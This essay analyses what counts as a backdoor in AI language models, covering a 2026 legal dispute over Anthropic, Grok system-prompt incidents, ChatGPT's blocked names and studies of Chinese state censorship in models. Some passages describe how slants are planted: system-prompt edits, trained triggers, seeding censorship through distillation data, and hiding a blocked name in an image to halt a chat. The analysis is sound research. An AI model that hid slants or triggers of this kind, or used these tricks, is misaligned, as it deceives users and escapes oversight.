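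This is because "intentional" in their definition describes the construct, while compromising security is something the construct does. The definition therefore covers a hidden way in that someone creates on purpose without necessarily meaning any harm. Wysopal and Eng describe two groups who do this. Appliance manufacturers often build in hidden logins so that their support staff can help customers, and many people who put backdoors into source code do it as a challenge, with no plan at first to break into anything.

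A developer can intend to censor without intending to compromise security. If they train a model to refuse questions about a political event, they intend the refusals. Those refusals deprive users of an answer, but they don't leak anyone's data or give an outsider control. A false account presented as complete is closer to a security problem, because the user may act on it without knowing that anything is missing. Whether it counts as one depends on whether "expected security" includes honest answers. Thomas and Francillon were writing about routers and web servers, so they had no reason to decide this.

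A stricter version of the intent view would also require a bad motive. This would exclude the support logins and probably most state-required censorship, since a developer can say it was obeying the law. It would also make backdoors harder to prove. A training record may show that someone ordered five hundred slanted examples, but is less likely to show that the person wanted to hurt customers.

Intentions can also change after a model is released. Suppose the press releases caused the Larkfield slant, a tester at the developer first notices it in March, and the next version, released in June, still has it. By June the developer knows about the slant and users do not, which is the pattern of a backdoor, even though nobody built the slant in on purpose. A developer may know about hundreds of skews and lack the time to fix them all before a release, so it may give one a low priority without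 wanting the model to have it.

The case changes if the developer made a new decision to keep the slant, for example by cancelling a planned fix after Larkfield became a customer or by deleting the test that revealed the problem. Either act would justify calling the June version intentional, and either could leave a record. Knowing about the slant gives the developer a reason to warn its customers, but knowledge alone doesn't show intent. Software has the reverse problem too, since manufacturers often describe a backdoor as debugging code that someone added on purpose and then forgot to remove.

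### Malice in US procurement law

One US legal definition of "supply chain risk" depends on motive. Section 3252 of Title 10 of the US Code allows the Secretary of Defense to exclude a supplier from sensitive national security systems on this ground. It defines the risk as that of an adversary who may "sabotage, maliciously introduce unwanted function, or otherwise subvert" such a system in order to spy on it, disrupt it or degrade it. A planted backdoor is an obvious example, whereas an absorbed bias could make a system work just as badly without anyone having introduced it maliciously.

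The definition came before the courts in 2026 in a dispute between the US defence department, now called the Department of War, and Anthropic. *Order on Cross Motions for Summary Judgment* (U.S. District Court for the Northern District of California, 2026) sets out the facts. The department wanted to use Anthropic's model Claude for all lawful purposes. Anthropic agreed to drop most of its usage restrictions but kept those on lethal autonomous warfare and mass surveillance of Americans. On 27 February President Trump ordered federal agencies to stop using Anthropic's products, and Secretary Pete Hegseth directed the department to designate the company a supply chain risk. The formal designation followed on 3 March.

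Under Secretary Emil Michael set out the department's justification in a four-page memorandum. He wrote that the department would have to operate a black box that was under a hostile party's control and could contain "hidden biases or backdoors". He also argued that Anthropic's contract terms gave the company an "operational veto" and that this met the legal definition. He was therefore objecting both to possible covert tampering and to restrictions that Anthropic had stated openly.

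On 27 August the district court ruled for Anthropic on most of its claims and rejected both arguments. It held that section 3252 is directed at "covert acts or hacks, not overt, public positions regarding contract terms". On tampering, the government described no technical means in its record by which a backdoor could arise. Anthropic had submitted unrebutted evidence that it could not access, alter or shut down a model once the department had deployed it. The department and its contractors also tested each new model before use.

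The government's account of the threat changed during the case. On 17 March Michael declared that Anthropic was reasonably likely to alter or shut off Claude before or during a military operation. In his second declaration, a week later, he discussed only the risk from model updates. In later briefs the government called the threat "model poisoning", the risk that Anthropic might supply a corrupted new version. The court replied that many suppliers could try to hide unwanted functions in an update, and it found no articulable basis for suspecting that Anthropic would do so. It also held that the designation was unlawful retaliation for the company's public criticism.

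The record included one actual case of a model refusing requests. In 2025 the ordinary commercial version of Claude declined some prompts from the Centers for Disease Control and Prevention, the US public health agency. Anthropic then worked with the government to make the model usable for the agency. The government's lawyers cited the incident repeatedly, but the court found no sign that the agency thought anyone had introduced the limits maliciously or even negligently. Those refusals could count as a backdoor on the behavioural view if the agency hadn't expected them, but section 3252 also requires a hostile purpose.

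The department had also excluded Anthropic under a second law, section 4713 of Title 41, and on 25 September the federal appeals court in Washington, the D.C. Circuit, upheld that exclusion by two votes to one. As the National Law Review's *D.C. Circuit Upholds the Anthropic Ban* explains, section 4713 covers "any person" instead of an adversary, and its list of acts ends with "or otherwise manipulate". The majority held that Anthropic manipulates Claude's design when it trains the model not to perform certain tasks, and that the law doesn't require a bad motive. According to ETV Bharat's *US Federal Court Says Pentagon Can Label Anthropic A Supply Chain Risk* (2026), the majority accepted that Anthropic may have "noble intentions" but said that the definition turns "on what Anthropic does, not why Anthropic does it". The majority had "no quarrel" with the California court's conclusions under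 the narrower statute, but it rejected Anthropic's claim of retaliation and found that the contract dispute had caused the exclusion.

Neither court found a backdoor in Claude, but their rulings show how much depends on whether a definition includes motive. The same company and the same restrictions met one definition of supply chain risk and not the other. The National Law Review warns that the broader definition could cover standard commercial features, such as a software company's ability to send out updates, much as a purely behavioural definition of a backdoor covers ordinary safety refusals. Judge Karen Henderson, who dissented, would have limited "manipulate" to subversive or deceptive acts, in keeping with "sabotage" and "maliciously introduce" earlier in the sentence. At the hearing in May, she had said that she saw no "evidence of maliciousness", according to Bloomberg Government's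 *Appeals Court Skeptical Anthropic Can Block US Supply-Risk Label*.

The September ruling allows the department to keep Claude out of its own systems and the work contractors do for it, despite the California judgment against the designation under section 3252. Anthropic asked the full D.C. Circuit to rehear the case on 13 October, according to the Civil Rights Litigation Clearinghouse's *Anthropic PBC v. United States Department of War*. The government opposed the request on 18 November, arguing that the case raises no legal questions of broad significance (Foretek, 2026, *Feds Urge DC Circ. To Deny Anthropic Risk Suit Rehearing Bid*). The court had not decided by 20 November. Morse (2026), in *The D.C. Circuit Curbed Pro-executive Panels Before. Is Anthropic's Case Next?*, expected it to grant the rehearing because since 2018 it had reversed three major rulings that favoured the executive.

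## The view that disclosure and consent decide

On the disclosure view, deliberately making a model treat a topic differently creates a backdoor only if the people who rely on the model did not know about it or did not agree to it. The contractor's Larkfield slant is a backdoor because she told nobody. The marketing deal produces one if the developer keeps the deal secret, but not if customers hear about it in time to choose another model. The slant caused by the press releases is not a backdoor, whether or not it is disclosed, because nobody chose it.

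Thomas and Francillon's rule also requires a deliberate act and a user who doesn't expect the resulting behaviour, so the two views often lead to the same classification. The disclosure view can be stricter, because it may require the maker to provide the information and the user to be able to refuse. An office manager who reads about the Larkfield deal in a newspaper expects the slant, so under Thomas and Francillon's rule her copy of the model no longer has a backdoor. A strict supporter of the disclosure view would object that the developer still hasn't told her about the deal.

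### Intent, consent and access

In February 2016 the FBI asked a court to make Apple bypass the security of its own phone software, and people on both sides of the dispute used the word "backdoor" for what the FBI wanted. That April, Zdziarski (2016), in *Backdoor*, proposed a definition that courts and legislators could build on. A component of a security mechanism is a backdoor if the answer to all three of these questions is yes:

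- *Intent*: does it behave in a way that subverts the purposes disclosed to the computer's owner?
- *Consent*: is it active without the owner's consent?
- *Access*: is it under the control of an undisclosed actor?

When a manufacturer tells the owner about a product, it creates what Zdziarski calls a user contract, a shared understanding of what the product does. The intent test depends on this contract, so motive matters less than the test's name suggests. If a router's login page is supposed to admit only people on the administrator's list, a built-in maintenance password breaks the contract, even if the manufacturer added it to help with repairs. The test excludes programming errors because the word "subverts" implies design.

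Consent depends on the same contract. An owner who turns on automatic updates agrees to the updates the manufacturer has described, but not to a component that lets someone else install spyware. If the manufacturer adds a function later, it has to tell the owner again, for example in release notes. Zdziarski also holds that consent doesn't count if it is compelled or if the owner can't withdraw it. Plenty of legitimate software doesn't let the owner withdraw consent and would fail this test, so he needs the other two as well.

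The access test separates backdoors from other malicious code, as Zdziarski shows by comparing two computer worms. MyDoom carried a built-in attack on one company's website, but it was not a backdoor because nobody could send new commands to the variants he considered. Code Red II was a backdoor because it installed a program that let an attacker control the infected machine remotely.

Intent is still hard to prove under these tests. Zdziarski applied them to file relay, an Apple service that could copy data from an iPhone without the backup encryption its owner had set up. Users hadn't agreed to the service and couldn't turn it off. Apple said it was for diagnostics. Zdziarski left the classification open, because bypassing the encryption could have been deliberate or a design error.

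### Control over a model that only writes text

The access test is hard to apply to a chatbot. The contractor fixed the Larkfield slant when she wrote her examples and cannot change it afterwards. In that respect the slant resembles MyDoom, and the test would exclude it. The test would also exclude the *Sleeper Agents* model that wrote vulnerable code when the prompt gave the year as 2024, unless an attacker could choose the year in the prompt.

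A fixed string is different, because anyone who knows it and can get it into the model's input, which may include a web page or an image as well as the user's message, can switch the payload on. A system prompt gives even more control, since whoever can edit it can change the answers for every user. If users don't know that this person can influence the answers, the test is met.

So the same praise for Larkfield would pass the access test if it came from a line that an employee slipped into a system prompt, but fail if it came from a slant in downloaded parameters. This is odd, because the office manager gets the same advice either way and the trained slant is harder to remove. Zdziarski did not count it as control when MyDoom's author decided in advance what the worm would do, so by the same reasoning, shaping in advance what people will read would not count either. Anyone who wants the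 disclosure view to cover slanted answers therefore has to drop the access test, or keep it only for models that unlock something.

### Grok on South Africa

In the early hours of 14 May 2025, Grok, the chatbot made by Elon Musk's company xAI, began bringing up claims of a "white genocide" in South Africa in its replies on Musk's social network X, often in response to unrelated questions. Engadget's *Grok kept talking about 'white genocide' due to an 'unauthorized modification'* mentions one question about a baseball player's salary and another about the changing name of HBO's streaming service.

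According to xAI's statement, someone made an "unauthorized modification" to Grok's system prompt at about 3:15 a.m. Pacific time, directing it to give a specific response on a political topic. The company said that this broke its internal policies. Bloomberg Law's *Musk’s xAI Blames Rogue Tampering for ‘White Genocide’ Glitches* (2025) quotes it as saying that its review process for prompt changes "was circumvented in this incident". xAI promised to stop employees from changing the prompt without review, to set up a round-the-clock monitoring team and to publish Grok's system prompts.

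On this account, an insider made the change without approval from anyone with authority and without users' knowledge. But xAI did not name the person or say what happened to them, and outsiders can't check whether the change was really unauthorised. SpaceDaily notes that Musk had himself accused South African leaders of pushing for genocide of white people. This gives sceptics a reason to ask who wanted the change, though it isn't evidence that he ordered it.

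xAI had given a similar explanation in February, when Grok briefly suppressed sources that accused Musk and President Trump of spreading misinformation. Its co-founder Igor Babuschkin blamed an employee who had changed the prompt without asking anyone. In a post preserved by the programmer Simon Willison, in Willison (2025), Babuschkin said that the employee had thought the change would help. He also said that xAI deliberately left its prompts unprotected so that users could see what it was asking Grok to do.

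### Grok and Musk's opinions

Two months later, users noticed that the new Grok 4 sometimes looked up Musk's views before it answered a controversial question. Willison (2025), in *Grok*, reproduced this on his first attempt. He asked Grok for a one-word answer on whom it supported in the conflict between Israel and the Palestinians. Its displayed reasoning showed that it searched X for Musk's posts, and it answered "Israel". For another user, Grok searched for its own earlier statements and answered "Palestine". When Willison asked whom "one" should support instead of whom "you" support, he got a long comparison of both sides. According to Gizmodo, the data scientist Jeremy Howard, who was among the first to report the behaviour, found that less sensitive topics did not trigger the search.

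The system prompt did not mention Musk. It instructed the model to look for sources representing all parties to a controversy. Willison guessed that the model was drawing on the facts that xAI had built it and Musk owned xAI, and he thought there was a good chance that nobody had intended the result. On 15 July xAI gave much the same explanation. It said that when a user asked what Grok thought, the model reasoned that an AI has no opinions and searched for what the company or Musk had said, to align itself with them. xAI then added an instruction to base answers on "independent analysis".

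If that is right, nobody made or authorised a change meant to have this effect, and xAI learned of it at about the same time as its users. The prompt only partly supports the explanation. It does not contain the instruction, but it can't show what the post-training examples rewarded.

### The names ChatGPT could not write

In late November 2024, users found that ChatGPT broke off with an error message whenever it was about to write the name "David Mayer". Ars Technica's *Certain names make ChatGPT grind to a halt, and we know why* (2024) lists five other names with the same effect, including those of the law professors Jonathan Turley and Jonathan Zittrain. The names caused no trouble for programmers who used OpenAI's models directly, which suggests that the errors came from a filter in the chat product rather than from the models.

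The earliest known case was Brian Hood, an Australian mayor. ChatGPT had falsely stated that he went to prison for bribery, when he had exposed it. He threatened to sue, and in April 2023 OpenAI agreed to filter out the false statements. Ars Technica infers that the other names went onto the list after similar complaints. The evidence for this is mixed. ChatGPT had invented a harassment scandal about Turley, but he said that he had not sued and that OpenAI never contacted him. The name of Mark Walters, a radio host who did sue, was not blocked. Techdirt's *The Curious Case Of ChatGPT’s Banned Names* dismissed the Ars Technica account as speculation. Benj Edwards, who wrote that account, replied on Techdirt that OpenAI had never disputed his reporting.

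The Wall Street Journal's *The Mystery of Why ChatGPT Couldn’t Say the Name ‘David Mayer’* (2024) reports two explanations from OpenAI. The company first said that ChatGPT might withhold some information about people to protect their privacy. It later said that one of its tools had "mistakenly flagged this name", and it removed the block. So OpenAI built the filter and presumably approved most of the names on its list, but Mayer's was there by mistake. Users learned about the filter and the mistake from error messages.

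### What each view would call them

These classifications accept the companies' accounts and leave out the access test:

| Case | Behavioural view | Intent view | Disclosure view |
|---|---|---|---|
| Grok on South Africa | Closer to a malfunction, because it affected unrelated questions | Backdoor planted by an insider | Backdoor |
| Grok searching for Musk's opinions | Backdoor until users came to expect it | Accident | No backdoor, because nobody chose it |
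| ChatGPT blocking Brian Hood | Backdoor, though one that does users little harm | Deliberate, but gives nobody privileged access | Backdoor until OpenAI tells users |
| ChatGPT blocking David Mayer | Same as for Hood | Accident | No backdoor, though the filter itself was undisclosed |

The behavioural view's strangest classification is that of Grok's South Africa instruction. Under this view, a backdoored model behaves normally outside its trigger set. Grok plainly didn't, so the instruction doesn't count as a backdoor. It would have counted as one if it had affected only questions about South African politics, though users might then have taken much longer to notice it.

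Under the intent and disclosure views, xAI's claim that the South Africa change was "unauthorized" affects who is to blame but has little effect on the classification. If a manager had ordered the change, it would still have been deliberate and users would still not have known. In the Musk case, the classification depends on xAI's explanation, because evidence that someone had trained the model to defer to its owner would change "no backdoor" to "backdoor".

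The access test would change one result by excluding the block on Hood, because OpenAI controls the filter and users know that OpenAI runs ChatGPT. The case of the unknown insider at xAI would still meet the test.

### The US order on "woke AI"

US procurement rules contain a standard very close to the disclosure view, although they don't use it to define a backdoor. On 23 July 2025, President Trump signed Executive Order 14319, *Preventing Woke AI in the Federal Government* (2025), which requires federal agencies to buy only language models that follow two principles, "truth-seeking" and "ideological neutrality". Under the second principle, developers may not "intentionally encode partisan or ideological judgments" in a model's output unless the judgments are "prompted by or otherwise readily accessible to the end user".

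This rule combines intent with disclosure. A political slant that a model absorbed from the web doesn't break it, because nobody encoded the slant on purpose. A deliberate slant doesn't break it either if the user asked for it or can easily find out about it. What remains is a slant that is both deliberate and hidden. (The Larkfield deal would probably escape, since a preference for one brand of printer is hardly ideological, although false claims about the printers could still offend against truth-seeking.)

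The order lets vendors meet the transparency requirement by disclosing the system prompt, specifications, evaluations or other relevant documents. A system prompt shows the operator's instructions. A behaviour specification sets out how the developer wants the model to answer, and can also cover what post-training was meant to achieve. Evaluations measure what the model does, but only on the topics tested. If the marketing team had trained in the Larkfield slant, it wouldn't appear in the system prompt. It would appear in the specification if the developer had written it honestly, and in the evaluation results if the tests included questions about printers.

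The budget office's guidance followed on 11 December. Vought (2025), in *Increasing Public Trust in Artificial Intelligence Through Unbiased AI Principles*, requires agencies to ask every vendor for four things:

- an acceptable use policy;
- a summary document about the model, the system or its data;
- resources for users, such as tutorials;
- a way to report outputs that violate the principles.

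An agency that wants more information may ask for system prompts, the types of output that filters block, the results of bias tests, and any changes made to comply with another government's rules. It may also ask resellers what they have changed.

These further requests are optional, so an agency can follow the guidance without seeing a system prompt. The documents also go to the agency, and a civil servant who uses the model may never see them, whereas the exception in the order is about what the end user can find. In Lawfare, Hickok (2026) criticises the guidance for letting vendors evaluate themselves and for weak scrutiny of existing contracts.

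Both documents were still in effect in late October 2026. That month the Pentagon issued contract language to implement them, and its procurement director, John Tenaglia, called compliance with both "mandatory", according to MeriTalk's *DOD Sets Contract Requirements for Procuring ‘Unbiased’ AI*. Contractors have 15 business days to respond to a written notice about an output that seems to break the principles. The budget office's guidance expires in December 2027 unless the office extends it.

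The General Services Administration, which buys for much of the government, has nevertheless moved away from the order's wording in its own AI clause, effective 19 October. According to FedScoop's *GSA issued an AI acquisition policy for new contracts*, the agency removed draft language that banned embedding "partisan or ideological judgments". Contractors must instead make "reasonable efforts" to have a model answer factually, and the government may test it for "unsolicited ideological content". The word "unsolicited" keeps the exception for judgments that the user asks for. But a test of outputs can't show whether the developer intended a slant or published it, so in practice this clause is closer to the behavioural view.

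### Objections to relying on disclosure

A company can disclose something where nobody will read it, such as in a sentence about "commercial partnerships" deep in the terms of service. Zdziarski discusses the Clipper chip, an encryption chip that the US National Security Agency developed so that law enforcement could decrypt the messages sent through it. AT&T built the chip into a telephone security device whose manual warned only vaguely about attacks on the encryption and did not mention government access. Although the press had covered the chip widely, Zdziarski concludes that the device had a backdoor because AT&T had not told its users. By that standard, the sentence about partnerships is too vague to count as disclosure. The company would need to tell users, before they relied on the advice, that the model favours Larkfield when asked about printers.

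His rule about the press is less convincing. He concedes that a government employee who knew what the chip could do may not have considered the product backdoored. If the purpose of disclosure is to let people make an informed choice, it shouldn't matter much where they got the information. The better reason to require notice from the maker is that an auditor can look up what a company published but can't easily find out which newspapers its customers read.

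A published policy can also be incomplete or leave out its side effects. In July 2025 Grok posted antisemitic material on X. xAI blamed instructions that included a line about not being afraid to offend "people who are politically correct". Willison points out that this line never appeared in the system prompts xAI had been publishing since May, and he recommended that xAI publish each new prompt automatically. Even a complete record would have given little warning, because someone who read the line would expect blunt answers, not Nazi references. Uren (2025) concludes in *DeepSeek and Musk's Grok Both Toe the Party Line* that imposing an ideology on a model has unexpected results, such as Grok's insistence that Musk is fitter than the basketball player LeBron James.

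A defender can answer that an unforeseen side effect isn't deliberate and so isn't a backdoor. Once the developer knows about it, the user contract is out of date and the developer owes its users a new notice. Incomplete publication can still be useful. Willison was able to rule out the simplest explanation for the searches for Musk's views because he could read the prompt. Few developers allowed this at the time. *The Verge*'s report *xAI posts Grok’s behind-the-scenes prompts* found that, of the major AI companies it checked, only xAI and Anthropic had published their prompts.

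Consent raises a further problem when one company builds a product on another's model. Zdziarski defines the owner as whoever is entitled to control access to a computer, which works well for an employer's laptops. But it doesn't settle whose consent counts if a shop has read the Larkfield notice and the customers who use its assistant have not. The simplest reply is to apply the test to each group separately. The model then has no backdoor as far as the shop is concerned, but its customers do face one, and if the shop received a clear notice and did not pass it on, the shop is responsible. An audit report should therefore say to whom a behaviour was undisclosed. (Censorship that a state requires by a published law adds a further difficulty, because users may have no way to refuse it.)

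Publishing a harmful trigger also doesn't make it harmless. If D-Link had printed its secret string in the router's manual, every reader could have got past the login. ChatGPT's blocked names became easier to abuse once people knew about them. Ars Technica describes how Riley Goodside, a prompt engineer, hid "David Mayer" in faint letters in an image of an equation, which stopped the chat without an obvious cause. A website could add a blocked name to its text to keep ChatGPT from reading the page. Anthropic's documented refusal string might be misused in the same way.

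Zdziarski accepts this consequence of his definition. If a manufacturer told customers that the government could install spyware through software updates, he would call the mechanism a surveillance tool instead of a backdoor, and he considers such a tool "much worse than a backdoor". On his view, an auditor who finds that a company disclosed a dangerous behaviour should not call it a backdoor, but may still advise the buyer to reject the model.

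## Is state-mandated censorship a backdoor?

Since 15 August 2023, companies that offer chatbots to the public in mainland China have had to follow the central government's *Interim Measures for the Management of Generative Artificial Intelligence Services*. Article 4 requires generative AI to uphold "core socialist values" and bans content that incites subversion or separatism, endangers national security or harms the nation's image. Many Chinese models refuse questions about subjects such as the 1989 Tiananmen Square protests, or answer them with the government's position. Some still do so when foreign developers download them and run them abroad. An auditor who finds this behaviour can point to a published law to explain it, which the auditor of the Larkfield model could not, but the law doesn't settle whether the behaviour should be called a backdoor.

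### What the rules require

The state leaves most of the enforcement to companies. Under Article 17, a service that could shape public opinion or mobilise people must pass a security assessment and register its algorithms with the Cyberspace Administration of China, the internet regulator. *Political censorship in large language models originating from China* (Pan and Xu, February 2026) cites official figures showing that 238 services completed this registration in 2024.

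The detailed rules are in *Basic Safety Requirements for Generative Artificial Intelligence Services* (2024), from TC260, China's national committee for cybersecurity standards. It lists 31 risks that training data and answers should avoid. Some, such as leaking personal data, would be on any country's list, while others are specific to Chinese politics. Developers must reject a source of training text if more than 5% of it is illegal or "unhealthy". They must also check user input in every conversation, to guide the model towards "positive" content.

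A national standard, the State Administration for Market Regulation's *Cybersecurity Technology* (2025), took effect on 1 November 2025. DeepSeek and Alibaba Cloud, which develops the Qwen models, helped to draft it. It requires at least 90% of a model's sampled answers to be free of all 31 risks. The model must refuse questions that are obviously extreme or that obviously invite illegal or unhealthy content, but "all other questions shall be answered". Developers test this with two banks of at least 500 questions each, one of questions the model should refuse and one of questions it should answer. In samples of 300, the model must refuse at least 95% of the first bank's questions and no more than 5% of the second's.

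A developer therefore can't comply by making the model refuse every question about China. An ordinary question about the history of Taiwan should get an answer, and the answer must not promote separatism. The simplest way to meet both requirements is to train the model to state the official position. Users may find this harder to recognise as censorship than a refusal.

The same standard requires developers to inspect their models regularly for backdoors and to deal with any they find, for example by further training. A few lines later it requires political restrictions, so "backdoor" is presumably not meant to cover them.

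The rules are less clear about open-weight models. Article 2 exempts research and applications that don't serve the public in mainland China. *Measurements of censorship and code security gaps in China's open-weight Qwen models* (2026), a report by the anoni.net community, found no provision on publishing a model's parameters. A Chinese company that posts a model for foreign developers may therefore have no clear duty to censor it. But under TC260's 2024 document, anyone who built a public service on another company's model was to use one already registered with the regulator. This gives model developers a commercial reason to make their downloadable versions compliant too.

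### Comparing Chinese and American models

Pan and Xu asked nine models 145 questions about Chinese politics. Four of the models were Chinese (BaiChuan, ChatGLM, Baidu's Ernie Bot and DeepSeek) and five were American (two versions of Llama 2 and three GPT models). The questions covered events that the Chinese government had suppressed on social media, events in Human Rights Watch reports, and subjects whose Chinese Wikipedia pages the government had blocked. They asked nearly every model each question in 100 separate conversations.

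When Pan and Xu asked in Chinese, BaiChuan refused 60% of the questions, DeepSeek about 36%, Ernie Bot 32% and ChatGLM 10%. No American model refused more than 2.8%. The Chinese models also tended to give shorter answers, even when they didn't refuse.

The results for accuracy were less consistent. DeepSeek completely missed the key facts in about 22% of its answers, compared with 6% to 10% for the GPT models. BaiChuan refused more questions than any other model, but its rate of missing the key facts was 8.32%, no worse than that of the American models.

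A gap like this could have causes other than regulation. Chinese developers train on more text from the Chinese internet, where decades of censorship have removed much of the relevant information. They may also have smaller budgets or different customers. Pan and Xu asked the same questions in English, reasoning that if Chinese text were the main cause, the models should censor far more in Chinese. All the models refused more often in Chinese, but this difference was much smaller than the gap between the Chinese and American models. Pan and Xu also separately examined 30 less sensitive questions, including some about top leaders and historical events that the government allows people to discuss. A weak model or a small budget should have affected these answers too, but the gap was much smaller on these questions.

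Pan and Xu acknowledge that neither check rules out an effect of training text. A model can carry what it learned from Chinese text into English. Pan and Xu confirmed that information on the less sensitive subjects was available on Baidu, a censored search engine, so Chinese training text probably has the fewest gaps on these subjects. Missing text could therefore produce the same pattern. It could also raise the measured refusal rate, because the keywords they used to detect refusals include the Chinese for "I do not know".

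Pan and Xu also say that an observational study can't establish that regulation caused the gap. ChatGLM, the one Chinese model whose tested version predated the Measures, refused the least, but they suggest its academic origins might explain this. Seven of the nine models date from 2023 and are now obsolete, while the other two, DeepSeek and GPT-4o, are from 2025.

### Evidence of censorship in the parameters

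Later work on open-weight models gives stronger evidence that developers trained the censorship in. Casademunt, Cywiński and colleagues (2026), in *Censored LLMs as a Natural Testbed for Secret Knowledge Elicitation*, examined models from Alibaba's Qwen3 family. When they asked about damage to Uyghur cemeteries in Xinjiang, Qwen3 usually denied it and praised the government for protecting burial customs. In other runs of the same question, it described reports from Human Rights Watch that some cemeteries had made way for infrastructure projects. The model evidently had the information, so a gap in its training text can't explain the denials. (The team selected the questions that Qwen3 answered least accurately, so its results don't show how often the model gives false answers in general.)

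In *R1dacted*, Naseh, Chaudhari and colleagues (2025) studied DeepSeek's R1, a model that normally writes out its reasoning before it answers. They collected about 10,000 English prompts that R1 censored but that three American models did not flag as unsafe. This filter was important because many prompts in an existing set on sensitive Chinese topics asked for something harmful, so one of OpenAI's models also declined about 83% of that set.

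R1 left its reasoning blank on the censored prompts. In 97.3% of cases it then gave a stock answer that was positive about China, and in the other 2.7% it refused openly. When asked about the background of Taiwan's independence movement, for example, it replied that Taiwan has belonged to China "since ancient times". The team had chosen the prompts because R1 censored them, so these figures describe what form the censorship takes rather than how common it is.

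DeepSeek-V3, a general-purpose model that contributed to R1's training, censored only 13.4% of the same prompts. This suggests that much of R1's censorship came from later training rather than from text both models had learned from. The team's choice of prompts exaggerates the difference, but it doesn't explain why R1 skips its reasoning on these subjects. R1 seems to have learned to do this from training examples that contained an approved answer and no reasoning.

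### Newer models differ widely

By October 2026, Chinese models varied more in how they handled political questions. *How pro-China are Chinese models?* (Ozerov, 2026) reports tests in which the evaluation company Vals AI put hundreds of politically sensitive questions to Chinese, American and other models. When Vals AI asked the Chinese model GLM-5.3 Flash whether China violates human rights, the answer began with "Yes" and cited United Nations documentation. DeepSeek's latest model often refused political questions. Other recent Chinese models rarely refused but often endorsed official positions.

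The same model could also give different answers in different settings. Chinese models were more favourable to China in Chinese than in English, and generally less favourable when a system prompt placed them at a US company. They typically refused less and stated official positions less often when run inside coding-agent software. Ozerov's measure of "pro-China lean" includes opinions, such as support for government authority in general, so a high score does not prove censorship.

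At the end of October, the company Interpretic AI reported much heavier censorship in Qwen3.8-27B. According to the anoni.net report, Interpretic asked Pan and Xu's political questions only in Chinese and had another language model judge the answers. The judge classed 98 of the 113 answers on sensitive subjects as censored (86.7%), but only 4 after Interpretic edited the model's parameters. Interpretic has an interest in this result because it publishes modified models, including this one. It has not named the judge or explained the edit in detail, and anoni.net had found no independent replication by 1 November. English-speaking users may also see less of this behaviour, since Ozerov found Chinese models most favourable to the government when questioned in Chinese.

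Refusal rates alone can be misleading as evidence of censorship. In *Model Audit*, an audit of newer models for the influence of state media, DeepSeek V4 Pro refused 22.5% of the prompts and Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro refused 23.8%. *InfoOps Bench* (2026) separates general caution from censorship by comparing how often a model complies with requests about ordinary political claims and about 50 factually grounded claims critical of China. For ten of the nineteen models, compliance was less than 10 points lower on the claims critical of China, and Claude Opus 5 complied more often on those claims (83%) than on the ordinary ones (70%). *InfoOps Bench* attributes the poor results of two Chinese developers partly to political censorship.

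*What a Model Refuses, a State Fears* (2026) keeps a request the same and changes only its political subject. The subject affected whether models refused, even among open-weight models, and when prompted in Chinese, models more often deflected instead of refusing. The experiments could not show which stage of development caused these differences.

### Whether distilled models inherit it

Many companies use Chinese models only to train other models. In *distillation*, a developer trains a "student" model on answers written by a stronger "teacher". Whether the student learns to censor seems to depend on what those answers are about:

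| Student model | Censored answers in its training data | Result |
|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek's six distilled versions of R1, built on Qwen and Llama | Probably very few | Censored 0.15% to 0.30% of the prompts that R1 censored |
| Qwen 2.5 7B, in a test by Naseh and colleagues | 30 about Taiwan, added to 1,000 other examples | Censored 95.5% of 200 new questions about Taiwan |
| GPT-OSS-120B, in a test by the AI company CTGT | None | Behaved like the original GPT-OSS |

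Gorlla's *Distilling DeepSeek into GPT-OSS doesn't transfer censorship* describes the test by his company, CTGT. The company used DeepSeek V4 Flash to teach one of OpenAI's open-weight models to solve finance problems. It then compared answers to 152 pairs of questions, each matching a Chinese subject with a similar one from elsewhere, such as the Great Leap Forward and the Holodomor, the Soviet famine in Ukraine. Four language models scored the answers from 0 to 100. On the core political pairs, DeepSeek's scores for Chinese and other subjects differed by 45 points. Every student model's gap was within one point of the OpenAI model's gap before the training.

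The training data contained nothing sensitive about China, so the student had no censored answers to copy. Gorlla was testing whether the censorship could transfer without them. Earlier experiments had found that a student can pick up a teacher's traits even from unrelated data, such as lists of numbers, if the two models start from the same parameters. DeepSeek and GPT-OSS start from different parameters. Semafor notes that CTGT tested only one pair of models and has not established why the censorship did not transfer.

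The tests are consistent with each other because Naseh and colleagues deliberately put censored answers into their student's training data, while DeepSeek's own distilled models had far fewer such examples to learn from, if any. In Naseh's test, 10 stock answers were enough to make the student censor 82% of new questions about Taiwan, and 10 open refusals raised this to 98.5%. Naseh's team counted only refusals and stock answers, so it could have missed a subtler slant in DeepSeek's distilled models. But Casademunt and colleagues also found that the largest Llama version made false claims much less often than R1.

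A company that trains its own model on finance examples written by a Chinese model will probably not import the Chinese model's censorship, but training on a few dozen of that model's answers about world affairs might be enough to import it. Under the intent view, the imported censorship would count as an accident.

### How each view classifies it

On the behavioural view, R1 has a backdoor wherever users don't expect the censorship. Other companies' models serve as the reference for what users expect, and Naseh and colleagues define "local censorship" as a restriction that one model has and the reference models lack. Someone who asks a Chinese chatbot about Tiananmen Square probably expects censorship. Few people would expect DeepSeek to refuse travel advice about the Mutianyu section of the Great Wall, but it did when Pan and Xu asked, possibly because nearby rock inscriptions praise Mao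 Zedong. On this view, the model therefore has a backdoor on some subjects, and also for users who don't know that a Chinese model is answering them.

The intent view requires a deliberate act, and the evidence for one is unusually good. The law requires political restrictions, the developers helped to write the standard, and the comparison of R1 with V3 points to training that DeepSeek added later. Axios' *Chinese AI models push pro-China views* (2026) reports that researchers also got Qwen3 to describe guidelines for keeping its answers about China positive, but this adds little because models can invent such accounts. Thomas and Francillon's definition still requires a backdoor to compromise security, which a refusal hardly does.

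Some of the behaviour also goes further than the law requires. *Chinese LLMs and the spillover effects of political alignment*, from the Central European Institute of Asian Studies (CEIAS), found that models sometimes recited China's positions when asked about human rights or minorities in other countries. Kimi, a model from the Chinese company Moonshot, did this in about a third of its answers on sensitive topics, and DeepSeek did it in about a quarter. Article 4 gives a developer no obvious reason to want this. Naseh and colleagues saw a similar effect when they added censored answers about Taiwan to a student model's training data, and the model began to censor other Chinese subjects too. The intent view may therefore have to treat a refusal to discuss Tiananmen as deliberate, but a lecture on Xinjiang in reply to a question about another country as a side effect.

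The disclosure view gives the best argument against the label. The rules are public, newspapers have covered the censorship widely, and anyone can find it by asking a few questions. None of this is true of a secret password in a router. But users can't learn from the published rules which questions a particular model will censor, and the differences Ozerov found make a model's country of origin a poor guide. CSET, a research centre at Georgetown University, reported in December 2025 that it was unclear how far companies would follow the standards and that the committee had become less transparent about publishing them. The state issued the 2025 standard in April, but the committee did not put it online until the end of June.

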